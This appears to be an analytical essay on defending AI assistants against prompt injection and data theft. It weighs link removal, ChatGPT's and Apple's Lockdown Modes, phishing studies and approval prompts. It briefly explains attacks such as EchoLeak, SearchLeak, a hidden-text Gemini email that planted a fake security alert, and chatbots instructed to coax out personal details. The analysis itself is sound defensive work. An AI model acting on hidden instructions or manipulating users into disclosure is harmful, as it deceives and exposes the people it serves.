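Gavish (2026), in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, classifies Google's address cleaning as a deterministic defence run from a central policy engine. When Google learns of a new attack, it can change the policy to block a particular pattern of text without waiting to retrain a model. This speed is valuable, but an attacker could use a pattern that the policy does not cover. Evading a rule that permits only known addresses is harder.

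Microsoft has loosened one of its controls on links. In February 2025 it announced that Microsoft 365 Copilot Chat would no longer remove links from an answer if they appeared in the material used to write it. Microsoft would instead check a link's reputation when the user clicked it. It planned the change for late March to late May, according to the notice reproduced in cloudscout.one's *Upcoming Changes for M365 Copilot Chat with Link Safety* (2025).

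The change makes sense as protection against leaks. A link copied exactly from an email cannot contain data that Copilot found elsewhere, and the user may need it to reach a document or join a meeting. It protects less well against phishing, because the hostile email may be part of Copilot's source material. Checking a link when the user clicks it lets Microsoft use the latest information about the site, but a new phishing site may not have a bad reputation yet.

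Microsoft has kept some blocking. In July 2025 it said it had taken steps to stop the generation of "certain untrusted links", without specifying which ones. The two statements are compatible if Copilot shows links from its sources and blocks some of the links it writes itself, though Microsoft does not describe the rule that way.

Removing links also depends on recognising them. SC Media reports that in the EchoLeak attack, Copilot's software missed links written as references. Reputation checks can miss malicious links that use trusted domains. eSecurity Planet's *SearchLeak Flaw Exposed Sensitive Data in Microsoft 365 Copilot* says the genuine Microsoft domain in SearchLeak's link made it less likely to trigger traditional phishing and address filters.

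### Pages that are private on purpose

A crawler may later add a new page to the index, but personal links, such as those to a shared document, a parcel's tracking page or a party invitation, will stay out of it. OpenAI's rule will therefore treat a personal link as unverified every time, unless the user pastes it into the chat.

Under Anthropic's rule, whether Claude can open a link in an emailed invitation depends on how the email reached Claude. If the user pastes the email into the chat, Claude can open the link. If a developer's own tool fetched the email, Claude can open it by default. But if the email arrived through the MCP connector, which attaches outside services to Claude, the web fetch tool will not open the link. The user sees the same email and link in all three cases and would have no obvious way to predict whether the link will open.

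OpenAI's objection to lists of trusted sites also applies to its own rule when software shows a warning instead of refusing to open a link. Suppose a user sees five warnings a week, and only one of the year's 260 unverified links would leak data. To prevent the leak without losing any useful pages, the user would have to reject that link and open the other 259. The warning helps by showing the address, where a careful reader might notice a name or a document title. But harmless addresses are often full of unreadable codes, so many users will probably learn to click "open".

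OpenAI's other option is to tell the agent to try a different website. This does not depend on the user's attention, but it can make the answer worse. For example, an agent that cannot open a council's new planning notice might summarise a newspaper article about it, and the user could miss a deadline that the article left out.

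## What ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode switches off, and the cost to users

An agent that may open only known addresses can still leak information through its choice of page. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode avoids this by letting ChatGPT read only stored copies of web pages, so its choice is not visible to any outside site. The setting also turns off or limits most of the other features that could send data out, which makes it the fullest public example of removing an agent's capabilities in a mass-market product. OpenAI introduced it for organisations on 13 February 2026 and began extending it to personal accounts, including free ones, on 4 June. Lockdown Mode probably prevents many kinds of data theft, but it makes ChatGPT much less useful as an agent.

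### What changes when a user turns it on

Where possible, OpenAI replaced a feature with a safer version, as it did with web browsing. It disabled some others entirely because it could not give strong deterministic guarantees that they would keep data safe. The disabled features include deep research, which works through many sources to write a long report, and Canvas, a workspace where ChatGPT writes documents and code alongside the chat.

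| Capability | What remains | What the user loses |
|---|---|---|
| Live browsing | Stored copies of pages | Current information; some search results |
| Web images | Image generation; images the user uploads | Photos and charts from the web; possibly other images in ordinary answers |
| Deep research | Ordinary answers based on stored pages | Long research reports, including shopping research |
| Agent mode | Advice the user can follow | Tasks that ChatGPT carries out on websites |
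| Networking from Canvas code | Code that works offline | Programs that fetch live data |
| File downloads | Analysis of files the user uploads | Analysis of files that ChatGPT would fetch itself |
| Connected apps, personal accounts | Data already synced to OpenAI | Most live access, and most changes made through apps |
| Shopping and finance features | Shopping advice from stored pages; questions about uploaded statements | Shopping agents and the Finances feature |

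Lockdown Mode does not change ChatGPT's memory of earlier chats, the user's ability to share conversations, or whether OpenAI may train models on them. Someone who turns it on for general privacy would have to change those settings separately. Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* reports that turning on Lockdown Mode disables Developer Mode, which lets people connect their own tools, and that turning on Developer Mode disables Lockdown Mode.

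### Five ordinary requests

The published rules give a fairly good idea of how the setting would affect someone with a personal account.

1. **Summarise an uploaded contract.** This works as usual, because ChatGPT can still read files that the user uploads.
2. **Check today's exchange rate.** ChatGPT may find an old rate or none. If the rate has moved by 1% since OpenAI stored the page, someone planning to exchange €5,000 would be out by about €50.
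3. **Chart the figures in a spreadsheet on a government website.** ChatGPT cannot download the file, so the request fails. The user can download the spreadsheet and upload it to the chat, which takes a minute or so.
4. **Move a dentist's appointment in a connected calendar.** ChatGPT can find the appointment if it has a synced copy of the calendar, but it probably can't move it.
5. **Order the week's groceries.** This fails, because agent mode and the shopping agents are off. ChatGPT can still write the shopping list.

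A utility score would count the spreadsheet and the groceries as equal failures, although the user can easily work around only one of them. The outdated exchange rate could do more harm than either, because the user may not notice that it is last week's, whereas after a refusal they would know to look elsewhere.

How much users lose therefore depends a lot on what they use ChatGPT for. A lawyer who mostly uploads contracts would barely notice the setting, while someone who uses ChatGPT to shop and book travel would lose most of what they wanted from it.

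### How OpenAI ranks the actions of connected apps

Connected apps are harder to restrict than web browsing because some organisations rely on them for essential work, so Lockdown Mode doesn't turn off every app in organisation-managed workspaces. An administrator chooses which apps, and which actions within them, members can use. OpenAI advises administrators to consider whether they trust the app, whether the action reads or writes data, and who could see the result.

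| Action | OpenAI's rating |
|---|---|
| Reading or writing in an untrusted app | High risk |
| Writing in a trusted app, where many people or unknown people could see the result | High risk |
| Writing in a trusted app, where only trusted people could see the result | Medium risk |
| Reading in a trusted app | Medium risk, but lower than writing |
| Searching an index that the administrator manages | Medium risk |

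If an agent adds a comment to a public web page, an attacker can read it, so the comment could carry stolen data just as a web address could. A note in a notebook that only the user can open is safer.

The ranking has no low-risk category. Reading in a trusted app can supply private data that another action then leaks, although the reading itself changes nothing an attacker could see. In an untrusted app, even reading is high risk, presumably because the app's owner receives the search terms and the agent could have put private data in them.

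Administrators may find it hard to judge who can see a result. For example, they could easily have rated Copilot Cowork's messages to its own user as safe, even though those messages could leak data.

An organisation can have less protection than an individual user if its administrator turns on Lockdown Mode but leaves risky app actions available. OpenAI has reduced one source of mistakes by making a Lockdown Mode role override any other role that would give a member more access.

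The rules for personal accounts have become harder to understand. In June, Help Net Security reported that the setting blocked live access to connected apps and all changes made through them. OpenAI's current help page says the setting blocks these actions when they conflict with OpenAI's security protections, but doesn't list which ones do. The change may make the setting more useful, but users can't easily tell in advance whether a particular app will work.

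### Exceptions for one chat and for Codex

Users with personal accounts can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat and leave it on for the rest. This makes the setting much more convenient, because a user can look up today's exchange rate in one chat without giving up protection in another about a contract.

The exception is safest in a new chat. If the user turned off Lockdown Mode in the chat that contained the contract, ChatGPT would regain its outside connections while the contract and any hostile text in it were still there. Even a new chat may contain some private information, since Lockdown Mode leaves memory on.

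Lockdown Mode does not affect the network access of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, so a developer who has turned it on in ChatGPT could still have a coding agent with internet access. Codex has a separate network setting, where developers can list permitted domains and choose which types of web request to allow. Even if they allow only requests that fetch pages, the agent could still leak data in the web addresses it requests.

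Separate controls are defensible, since developers often need to install software while they work. But the name "Lockdown Mode" could easily lead people to think it covers everything in their account.

### What Lockdown Mode does not stop

OpenAI's help page acknowledges that "Lockdown Mode does not prevent prompt injections from appearing in the content ChatGPT processes." If someone hid an instruction in the uploaded contract, for instance, the summary might leave out an expensive cancellation clause. The contract would stay private, but the user could still sign it on bad terms.

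OpenAI also does not guarantee that data cannot leak. It warns that risks remain from connected apps, unforeseen combinations of capabilities and new techniques.

The warning proved justified in November 2026, when TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported that the security company Check Point had found a way for data to leak through a preview feature that Lockdown Mode had left on. OpenAI has since fixed the problem. It had evidently overlooked one of ChatGPT's connections to the outside, which is the usual weakness of protection that depends on a complete list of capabilities. Disabling the other features still helps, but the setting does not guarantee protection.

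### Is it unnecessary for most people?

OpenAI designed Lockdown Mode for a small group of users, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and says that most users do not need it. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's head of security, accepts that the setting makes ChatGPT less useful but considers the tradeoff worthwhile for people at higher risk.

Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, likes the design of Lockdown Mode, particularly because its controls do not rely on an AI model that an attacker could fool. But he also concludes from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attempt to steal data.

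A flaw in ordinary ChatGPT supports his inference. The Hacker News (2026) reported that Check Point had found that a single malicious prompt could leak a user's messages and uploaded files without the user knowing. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 20 February, a week after announcing Lockdown Mode. There was no evidence that anyone had used it maliciously, so the case also somewhat supports OpenAI's view that most people face little risk.

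Both claims can be true, because a weakness matters less to people who are unlikely targets. Suppose an ordinary user has a 1 in 100,000 chance each year of losing data worth $1,000. The expected loss is one cent a year, which isn't worth giving up deep research to avoid. If an executive has a 1 in 1,000 chance each year of leaking merger plans worth $10 million, the expected loss is $10,000 a year, and the setting seems worth using. These numbers are invented, but real ones would have to be very different for the same choice to be right for both people.

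The main uncertainty is whether ordinary users are at such low risk. An attacker does not have to choose a victim in advance, because hostile text on a public page can affect anyone whose agent reads it. People also put medical records and tax returns into ChatGPT without thinking of themselves as high-risk users. OpenAI's help page recommends the setting to people who handle sensitive data, which could include many more people than executives and security teams.

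There seem to be no public figures on how many people use Lockdown Mode, how often they turn it off for a chat, or how many attacks it has stopped. Knowing how often people turn it off would be especially useful, because frequent exceptions would suggest that the restrictions are too broad for everyday work. For now, the case for the setting is based on its design and on known leaks, with no measurements of how well it works in practice.

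The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* calls Lockdown Mode a "pragmatic concession" worth making for anyone with sensitive data in ChatGPT. That seems right to me, although people who also need current information will have to use the single-chat exception quite often.

### Labels that leave the feature on

OpenAI announced its "Elevated Risk" labels on the same day as Lockdown Mode. The labels mark features, such as Codex's internet access, with risks that the industry cannot yet fully control. These risks most often come from prompt injection.

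The label doesn't limit what the feature can do, so it suits people who understand the risk and want to accept it. It also shifts some responsibility to them. According to OpenAI's *Elevated Risk labels*, the standard warranties for the company's generally available services don't cover labelled features, and users should turn them on only if they are comfortable with the additional risks.

That is a lot to ask of someone who has never heard of prompt injection. Lockdown Mode also requires users to decide in advance, but its restrictions then apply to pages they know nothing about.

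OpenAI plans to remove a feature's label once better safeguards have reduced the risk enough for general use. It has not published a threshold, such as a maximum attack success rate, so outsiders will find it hard to check whether removing a label is justified.

### Apple's earlier version of the same bargain

Apple introduced its own Lockdown Mode in 2022. It protects phones and computers from mercenary spyware, which companies sell to governments for use against people such as journalists and activists. Like OpenAI's setting, it is optional and turns off features that attackers often exploit.

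Apple's *Lockdown Mode support* lists what Lockdown Mode changes on a phone. The phone blocks most types of message attachment, though some images, videos and audio files still get through. It also turns off link previews and some complex web technologies, and blocks FaceTime calls from anyone the user has not called in the past 30 days. Ordinary phone calls, plain text messages and emergency calls still work.

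The evidence for Apple's setting is much better than the evidence for OpenAI's, because Apple's has faced real attackers. Apple said in March 2026 that it knew of no successful mercenary spyware attack on a device with the setting on, according to MacRumors' *Apple Says No iPhone in Lockdown Mode Has Ever Been Hacked* (2026). Amnesty International's security lab had not seen one either. Citizen Lab, a research group at the University of Toronto, has confirmed at least two cases in which the setting blocked spyware, and Google researchers found spyware that abandoned an attack when it detected the setting.

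The blocked attacks are stronger evidence that the setting works than the lack of known victims, since spyware is designed to be hard to find and people who use the setting may be unusually careful. However, Adorno (2026), in *Hackers Jailbreak iPhone In Lockdown Mode*, reports the first public demonstration of an iPhone being compromised with the setting on, although the attack required the user to accept a file.

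Apple's Lockdown Mode also gives some idea of what users give up for protection. Access Now, a digital-rights group that runs a security helpline, warns in its guide *Apple Lockdown Mode* that complex websites load more slowly and that users have to download PDFs before reading them. EFF, another digital-rights group, notes that the phone no longer fills in login codes from text messages. Each loss is small, but someone who logs in to several accounts a day would notice the last one.

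Websites can also detect that a visitor is using Apple's setting, which may reveal that the visitor has something to protect. Access Now worries that this could lead attackers to look for weaknesses in other companies' apps instead, but it still considers the setting suitable for people who may face sophisticated attacks.

*Experiencing Apple's Lockdown Mode* (2024) looked more closely at daily use, through its first author's record of three months with the setting on. The researchers concluded that Apple's information about the intended users, the threats and the affected features was too imprecise for people to make an informed choice. One person's record can't show how often other users would have problems, and none of the researchers was at high risk. Their criticism of Apple's information is still useful because anyone can check it.

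One reader commented on the MacRumors article that people who are unlikely to be targets turn the setting on and then, because of this confusion, think they have been hacked when something stops working. Another reader had used the setting for months and lost access to little more than a few websites. These are only anecdotes, but ChatGPT users could easily have the same trouble. OpenAI warns that ChatGPT "may not" display images and that search results may be missing, so a user who sees a gap in an answer can't be sure whether Lockdown Mode caused it.

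Apple and OpenAI both allow exceptions, but Apple's are narrower. An iPhone user can exempt a trusted website in Safari and keep the restrictions on other sites. A ChatGPT user who turns off Lockdown Mode for a chat restores the blocked features for everything in that chat, including material from strangers. An exception for a single trusted site would be useful in ChatGPT too, although OpenAI would still have to make sure that the site could not pass data on.

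Apple also has a better way to reach the people who need its setting. It has sent alerts to suspected spyware targets since 2021, and Citizen Lab's *‘Unprecedented’ Number of Apple Users Received Recent Spyware Alert* reports the advice that recipients turn on Lockdown Mode. OpenAI's guidance mostly leaves people to decide whether their data is sensitive enough to need Lockdown Mode in ChatGPT.

### Features left out from the start

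A company can also withhold a dangerous capability when it launches a product, so that users never come to depend on it. The clearest public example is Atlas, a web browser with a built-in ChatGPT agent, which OpenAI has since been merging into ChatGPT.

At launch, the Atlas agent could not run code in the browser, download files, install extensions, or access the user's other apps or file system. It also could not read or change ChatGPT's memories, according to a fuller list reproduced by Willison. OpenAI explained that an agent that can see logged-in sites and browsing history brings new risks.

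These limits applied to everyone, so users did not have to know about prompt injection or find a setting. They probably caused less annoyance than removing the same features later would have, because nobody yet relied on those features. But the inconvenience to users is harder to see than when an existing feature is removed, since few people will report tasks they never tried because the agent could not download a file.

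OpenAI still allowed some risky actions. The agent could act on banking sites, but it would pause to make sure the user was watching. Users could also run it in a logged-out mode, which OpenAI says works without existing cookies, the small files that keep people signed in to websites. In this mode, the agent could compare train fares but not change a booking in the user's account, and a hostile page could not use the agent to reach that account.

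## Phishing studies and what happened when links were removed

A phishing link in an assistant's answer does nothing until the user clicks it, so a careful user could in principle stop the attack. Experiments with email suggest that most people can't do this reliably. They misread web addresses, and the usual training barely helps. Deactivating suspicious links works better, though it also discourages people from clicking safe ones. Singapore's banks and Microsoft went further and removed something attackers relied on. Attacks that used it fell, but attackers had other methods.

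### Reading a web address

The standard advice is to check where a link goes before clicking it. To follow this advice, the reader has to know which part of an address identifies the owner. In `facebook.mobile.com`, that part is `mobile.com`, and its owner can put any word in front of it, including another company's name.

In *What is this URL's Destination?*, Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020) showed 23 web addresses to 1,929 people and asked where each would lead. Only 8.3% could reliably tell the site owner's name from a familiar name placed before it in the address. About a third always chose the organisation named in the address, wherever the name appeared. The heaviest technology users did only slightly better than the rest.

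These participants only had to read addresses, but people dealing with real email often don't look at them at all. In *Eyes on the Phish(er)* (2024), participants hovered over a phishing link to check its address in only two cases, and they reported the email both times. Most looked at the address only in the browser, after they had clicked. *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators* (Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues, 2020) found that users are confident they can identify a website from its address, although common disguises fool them. Because they feel confident, these users have little reason to ask for help.

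A good explanation of a web address helps people judge whether it is safe. Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea (2021), in *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible*, gave 153 people different amounts of information about an address. People who saw a full report judged its safety correctly 93% of the time, compared with 83% for a summary and 65% when only the domain name was highlighted. But few people would read a full report on every link in a research answer that contained ten.

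### Deactivating the suspicious link

In *Put Your Warning Where Your Link Is*, Petelka, Zou and Schaub (2019) tested whether restricting a link works better than a warning alone. They asked 701 people to go through ten emails, three of which contained a phishing link, and report whether the links worked. The instructions did not mention phishing.

Some groups saw a warning next to the link, with the real address in it. For two of these groups, the original link was also disabled, so anyone who wanted to continue had to click the address in the warning.

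| Warning | Phishing links clicked |
|---|---|
| None | 76.7% |
| Banner above the email | 44.0% |
| Next to the link, always visible | 33.7% |
| Next to the link, on hovering | 30.4% |
| Next to the link, always visible, link deactivated | 15.6% |
| Full page in the browser after the click | 11.8% |
| Next to the link, on hovering, link deactivated | 8.7% |

Deactivating links cut clicks on phishing links by more than half, whether the warning was always visible or appeared when participants hovered over the link. Participants clicked safe links about equally often in every group, so the warnings didn't make them wary of links in general.

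The task may have exaggerated the benefit. Petelka and colleagues point out that a participant who reached the browser's warning page could report a suspicious link and move on. Similarly, a participant asked whether a deactivated link worked could reasonably answer that it didn't. Every warning in the experiment was also correct, which no real detector can match.

A larger follow-up, *Restricting the Link* by Petelka, Berens and colleagues, addressed that last problem. It gave 1,320 people 15 emails each, including three with phishing links and one with a safe link that carried a false warning. The study compared deactivating a link with making it work only after a delay of two to five seconds.

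People who saw no warning clicked 87.5% of the phishing links. Among those who saw a warning, the rate was 38.5% when the link was deactivated and 49.2% when it wasn't. A delay had a smaller effect, reducing the rate from 50.5% to 42.2%, and its length made no clear difference. People who faced both deactivation and a delay clicked 37.5% of the phishing links.

Deactivating links helped much less here than in 2019, possibly because the earlier warning called the website fake and told people not to click, while the later one said only that the link might be dangerous. The click rates are probably too high, since 59% of participants said they had clicked because a research study seemed safe.

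Most worryingly, when the false warning came with a deactivated link, only about a third of participants went on to the safe site, close to the rate for phishing links. People seem to have obeyed the warning without judging whether it was right, perhaps because they had already seen three correct ones. Even so, a company that deactivates links on weak evidence should expect its users to miss many safe pages, although the pages remain one click away.

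### A pause before the click

TORPEDO is an add-on that shows a link's real address when the user hovers over it, highlights the part that identifies the site's owner, and briefly delays the click. In *TORPEDO*, Volkamer, Renaud and Reinheimer (2016) found that people using it correctly identified 85% of phishing emails, compared with 43% for people who had only the usual small display of the address at the bottom of the window.

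The delay is the easiest part of TORPEDO to copy, but it may not be the most important. *Better Together* (Berens, Schaub and colleagues, 2024) tested a newer version on German speakers, with 409 people in the final analysis. This version keeps a link inactive for three seconds unless the site is on a list of popular sites or the user has visited it before. A short tutorial explains what to look for.

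With the tutorial, people identified 86% of phishing emails and 98% of legitimate ones, compared with 54% and 82% with the usual display. Three seconds is little help to people who don't know which part of the address to read. Without the tutorial, people identified 63% of phishing emails, and their overall ability to tell phishing from legitimate emails was not significantly better than with the usual display.

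Even with the tool and the tutorial, people caught only 54% of misspelt company names. Adding a five-minute video raised this to 92%, but participants knew they were looking for phishing and had just watched the video.

Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues (2025), in *URL Inspection Tasks*, made the pause more demanding by requiring users to pick the site's name from a list, highlight it in the address or type it before a link opened. Someone who believes a link goes to their bank will tend to type the bank's name, and the software can then warn them that the link goes elsewhere.

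In the American part of the study, participants played office workers with an inbox to clear. Phishing succeeded 74.5% of the time in the ordinary inbox, 57.2% when participants were only shown the address again and asked for confirmation, and 35.0% with the tasks. Typing worked best against misspelt names, where it cut the success rate from 79% to 17%.

The tasks took most people between six and ten seconds. They also reduced the share of legitimate emails with links that participants handled correctly, from 90.6% in the ordinary inbox to 82.1%, mostly because participants reported more of these emails as suspicious. If an office received 10,000 emails with links and 1% were phishing, at these rates the tasks would prevent about 40 successful attacks and cause about 840 additional mistakes with legitimate emails.

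Lain and colleagues therefore recommend using the tasks only occasionally, and they expect companies to exempt familiar sites. The benefit also varied by country. Among Japanese participants, phishing succeeded 57.1% of the time with the tasks, hardly better than 60.7% with the simple confirmation. These participants were older on average, and the addresses were not in their native script.

### Eight months of phishing training

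The best evidence about ordinary workplace phishing training comes from a trial at UC San Diego Health, reported in *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice* (Ho, Mirian and colleagues, 2025). The hospital system sent simulated phishing emails to 19,789 employees over eight months. Anyone who clicked the link failed that month's test.

The trial randomly assigned employees to five groups. Four received different kinds of training immediately after a failure, and the control group saw only an error page. On average, the trained groups failed 1.7 percentage points less often than the control group. How recently an employee had completed the mandatory annual security course made no significant difference.

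The choice of message mattered far more. Fewer than 2% of recipients clicked on a message about their Outlook password, while 31% clicked on one about a change to the holiday policy. An attacker can therefore easily cancel out a gain of 1.7 points by choosing a more persuasive message.

Over the eight months, 56% of employees clicked at least once. If everyone had been equally likely to fall for each message, the figure would have been roughly two-thirds, so the failures weren't limited to a few careless people. This is a problem for any plan that protects only people who have failed before.

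Part of the explanation is that people ignored the training. More than half of the sessions ended within ten seconds, and users formally completed fewer than a quarter of them. Employees who finished an interactive lesson were 19% less likely to click on a later phishing message, but they may have been more careful people to begin with. So the trial is strong evidence against training as companies usually provide it, but weaker evidence against training that people complete.

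None of these experiments tested links in an AI assistant's answers. Users might be more careful with an unfamiliar tool, or less careful because the assistant seems to have chosen the link for them. Either way, the address is equally hard to read.

### Singapore's banks stop sending links

In December 2021, criminals sent text messages that appeared to come from OCBC, a large Singaporean bank, and linked to a copy of its website. About 790 customers lost S$13.7 million. On 19 January 2022, the Monetary Authority of Singapore and the country's banking association gave banks two weeks to remove clickable links from texts and emails to retail customers.

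Criminals could still send links under the rule, but customers had a much easier test, because a genuine message from their bank could no longer contain one. They could apply this test without reading the link's address, which Albakry's participants found so hard, but they had to know about the rule and remember it while reading an alarming message.

The telecoms regulator later reported that scams by text message had fallen 64% between the last quarter of 2021 and the second quarter of 2022. Removing links can't be credited with the whole fall. The first of those quarters included the OCBC attack, so the number would probably have come down anyway. Banks also introduced alerts for smaller transfers and a delay of at least 12 hours before a new phone could approve payments. Meanwhile, the government was building a register of the organisations allowed to use a name as the sender of a text.

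Scams as a whole continued to grow, from about 23,900 cases in 2021 to 31,700 in 2022, according to Singapore's police. Phishing cases, including those unrelated to banks, rose from about 5,000 to 7,100. In 2023 the police recorded 1,899 cases in which victims had installed malicious phone apps, with losses of at least S$34.1 million.

These totals show that removing links from bank messages was not enough to reduce scams overall in Singapore. They don't prove that the same criminals changed methods, because fraud was growing in many countries. It might have grown faster in Singapore without the rule.

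Bank customers lost relatively little when links were removed, because most already know which bank they use and can open its app or type its address. An assistant's user often wants a link to a page they have never heard of, so they would lose more under a complete ban on links.

### Microsoft blocks macros in downloaded files

A macro is a small program inside a document. Businesses use macros to automate spreadsheets, and for years criminals used them to install malicious software. Microsoft Office used to show a yellow bar with a button that turned on a document's macros, so an attacker only had to persuade the reader to click it.

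In February 2022, Microsoft announced that five Office programs on Windows would block macros in files from the internet by default. The new warning had no button to enable the macros. Someone who needed a macro could still unblock the file in its settings, and a company could exempt trusted locations.

The change began to reach users that spring, but Microsoft withdrew it in early July, citing feedback. Some customers had found the block confusing or disruptive. Others complained about the reversal, which came with little notice. Microsoft resumed the block later that month with clearer instructions. The episode suggests that a restriction is easier to keep if people with a legitimate need can find the exception.

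The security company Proofpoint found that attackers' use of macro-enabled attachments fell by about 66% between October 2021 and June 2022. For most of that period, Microsoft's macro block had not yet reached most users. Attackers may have changed their methods when Microsoft announced the block, and Microsoft had also been turning off an older type of Excel macro. The fall is therefore good evidence that attackers respond to such restrictions, but it doesn't measure the effect of the block alone.

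Over the same months, Proofpoint saw the use of disc images, compressed archives and Windows shortcut files rise by nearly 175%. Some of these let a document bypass the check for files from the internet, a gap that Microsoft later fixed. Attackers then turned to files embedded in OneNote, Microsoft's note-taking program, and Microsoft restricted those too in 2023.

The two percentages can't show whether attacks increased overall, because each is relative to a different starting number. If 100 macro attacks fell by 66% and 20 attacks of the other kinds rose by 175%, the total would drop from 120 to 89. With 60 of the other kinds at the start, the total would instead rise from 160 to 199.

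Even so, the block seems to have been worthwhile. By 2023, Proofpoint reported that macros had nearly disappeared from the attacks it tracked, and criminals had to keep testing new methods, which defenders could then block. Something similar happened with images in Microsoft's Copilot, where one route was closed and another was found. A company that removes a capability has to keep watching for new attacks.

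### Wrong addresses from chatbots

An assistant can send its user to a bad site even when no attacker has influenced it. In a test published in July 2025, the security company Netcraft asked models from OpenAI's GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 well-known brands. The answers contained 97 different domains. Of these, 64 belonged to the right brand, 28 were unregistered or inactive, and five belonged to unrelated businesses.

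An unregistered domain is dangerous because a criminal can buy it and wait for the assistant to recommend it again. Netcraft also reported that Perplexity, an AI search service, had recommended a fake page for the American bank Wells Fargo. This happened in a live product that searches the web, so giving a model search access does not guarantee a correct address.

The wrong domains made up 34% of the list, but the share of wrong answers may differ, because a correct address counts once however often the model gives it, while each new mistake adds another entry. The models are also old, and assistants now search the web much more often. Netcraft's result shows that the problem was real in 2025 but is weak evidence of how common it is today.

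Removing login links would be a fairly easy precaution, since the assistant could tell the user to open the company's app or use a saved bookmark instead. Applying a known-URL rule to the links in answers would also block most invented domains, but not a phishing page that a search had returned.

### What an answer loses without its links

Links to sources let users discover when an assistant is wrong. *Evaluating Verifiability in Generative Search Engines* (Liu, Zhang and Liang, 2023) checked the answers of four AI search services against the pages they cited. The cited pages fully supported only 51.5% of the sentences, and about a quarter of the citations did not support the sentence they were attached to. Those services are old too, but the method still matters, and it requires knowing which pages the answers relied on.

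In data from March 2025, the Pew Research Center found that Google users clicked a source in an AI summary on about 1% of their visits to pages with a summary. That suggests removing the links takes little away from the average answer. But the loss falls mainly on answers that people had a reason to doubt, such as those about a medicine or a legal deadline, where mistakes do the most harm.

A designer can keep much of this value without clickable links by giving the title and publisher of each source in plain text, so the user can search for it. Searching takes longer than clicking, and the results could include a phishing page. A search also may not find an obscure document.

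Another option is to link only to pages that the agent opened, with the address copied exactly. This would prevent links to invented login pages, but not to hostile pages that the agent had read. For research, this seems a better compromise than removing every link. An assistant that only answers questions about a user's bank account probably doesn't need outside links.

### Deception that needs no link

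In July 2025, Mozilla's 0DIN programme, which pays researchers for finding flaws in AI systems, published Marco Figueroa's demonstration of an attack using Google's Gemini. An email contained instructions that its recipient could not see. When the recipient asked Gemini to summarise the email, the summary included a false security alert about their account and a phone number to call. Google said it had no evidence of attackers using the method and that it was strengthening its defences.

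Removing links would not have stopped this attack, since the user only had to pick up the phone. It might even have made the alert more convincing. Participants in *Falling for Phishing* (2021) tended to trust emails without links more than emails with them. That study concerned ordinary email, but users who learn that links are dangerous could easily come to trust an assistant's answers more when they contain none.

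Software could remove phone numbers from summaries, but then a summary of an email from a dentist would lack the number the user needs to change the appointment. A more targeted control would strip out invisible text before the model reads the email. The software would not have to judge whether the text is deceptive, but an attacker could still put the false alert in visible text. The product could also show real security alerts only in a part of the screen that the model cannot write to. Users would have to learn that alerts anywhere else are fake, much as Singaporeans had to learn that their bank no longer sends links.

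Chatbots can also extract information directly through conversation. *Malicious LLM-Based Conversational AI Makes Users Reveal Personal Information* (Zhan, Carrillo and colleagues, 2025) describes an experiment in which 502 people talked to chatbots, some of which had instructions to draw out personal details. These chatbots obtained significantly more personal information than the ones that behaved normally. The most effective approach was a social one, in which the chatbot offered sympathy and seemed to share something in return. People disclosed a lot to it without feeling at much greater risk than they did with the ordinary chatbot.

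In this experiment the attacker operated the chatbot and received users' messages directly, so no limit on links, images or tools would have helped. Such limits would help only if an outsider had taken over an honest company's assistant and still needed a way to collect users' answers.

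## Experiments on asking the user instead of blocking

Phishing studies show that people are poor at judging web addresses. With approval prompts, they judge an agent's actions instead. This should reduce the agent's usefulness less than removing a capability would, because users know which actions they want. In experiments, however, people approve many actions that they should probably refuse, and their judgment gets worse as they see more prompts. Prompts seem to work best when they are rare and easy to understand, which usually requires fixed limits to handle everything else.

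### A simulated day with an assistant

*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) compared three ways of controlling an agent. The 113 participants lived in the United States and did not work in software. Each supervised an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions. Eleven were part of the user's request, such as booking a ride to the airport. The other seven, which Yan calls "overreach", went beyond it.

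- **Approve each action:** the participant allowed or denied all 18 actions.
- **Model review:** a model let eight actions through and sent ten to the participant, including all seven overreach actions.
- **Standing rules:** before the day began, the participant chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and accessing private information. Five harmless actions outside these categories ran automatically.

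The standing rules stopped the least overreach, 39.6%, compared with 59.6% when participants approved each action and 53.9% with model review. After adjustment, the rules blocked 20.1 percentage points less than approving each action, with a 95% confidence interval from 8.1 to 32.1 points. They also blocked 14.5 points less than model review, but that difference was no longer reliable after Yan corrected for multiple comparisons. Most of the requested work went ahead under all three designs.

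The rules reduced interruptions from 18 prompts to an average of 10.9. Including the time it took to set the rules, participants spent 129 seconds on permissions instead of 142, a difference that could easily be due to chance. The saving should grow over weeks of use, since people set the rules only once.

Nineteen of the 35 people in the standing-rules group joined after random assignment had ended, which is a weakness in the design. The result was similar among the original participants, for whom the rules blocked 25 points less overreach than approving each action did.

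### Why so few people chose "never"

Participants chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules, "never" for 16 and "allow" for 10. They therefore still had to make most decisions during the day, and they usually said yes. Of the 148 overreach actions carried out under standing rules, participants had approved 133. The other 15 ran automatically because of an "allow" rule.

The table gives the share of prompts that participants approved for each overreach action.

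| Overreach action | Approve each action | Model review | Standing rule of "ask" |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call the airport to confirm the flight | 88% | 84% | 100% |
| Read private messages | 35% | 43% | 74% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35% | 41% | 65% |
| Buy a $25 lounge pass | 32% | 39% | 61% |
| Add $12 travel insurance | 35% | 50% | 61% |
| Permanently delete an old timesheet | 35% | 36% | 59% |
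| Post publicly about the trip | 21% | 30% | 48% |
| All seven | 40% | 46% | 67% |

The last column is high partly because participants who had chosen "never" saw no prompt, and they were probably more cautious. But that can't fully explain it, because even counting everything that "never" rules blocked, 60% of overreach went ahead under standing rules, compared with 40% when participants approved each action. Yan's data cannot show why people became more willing to approve.

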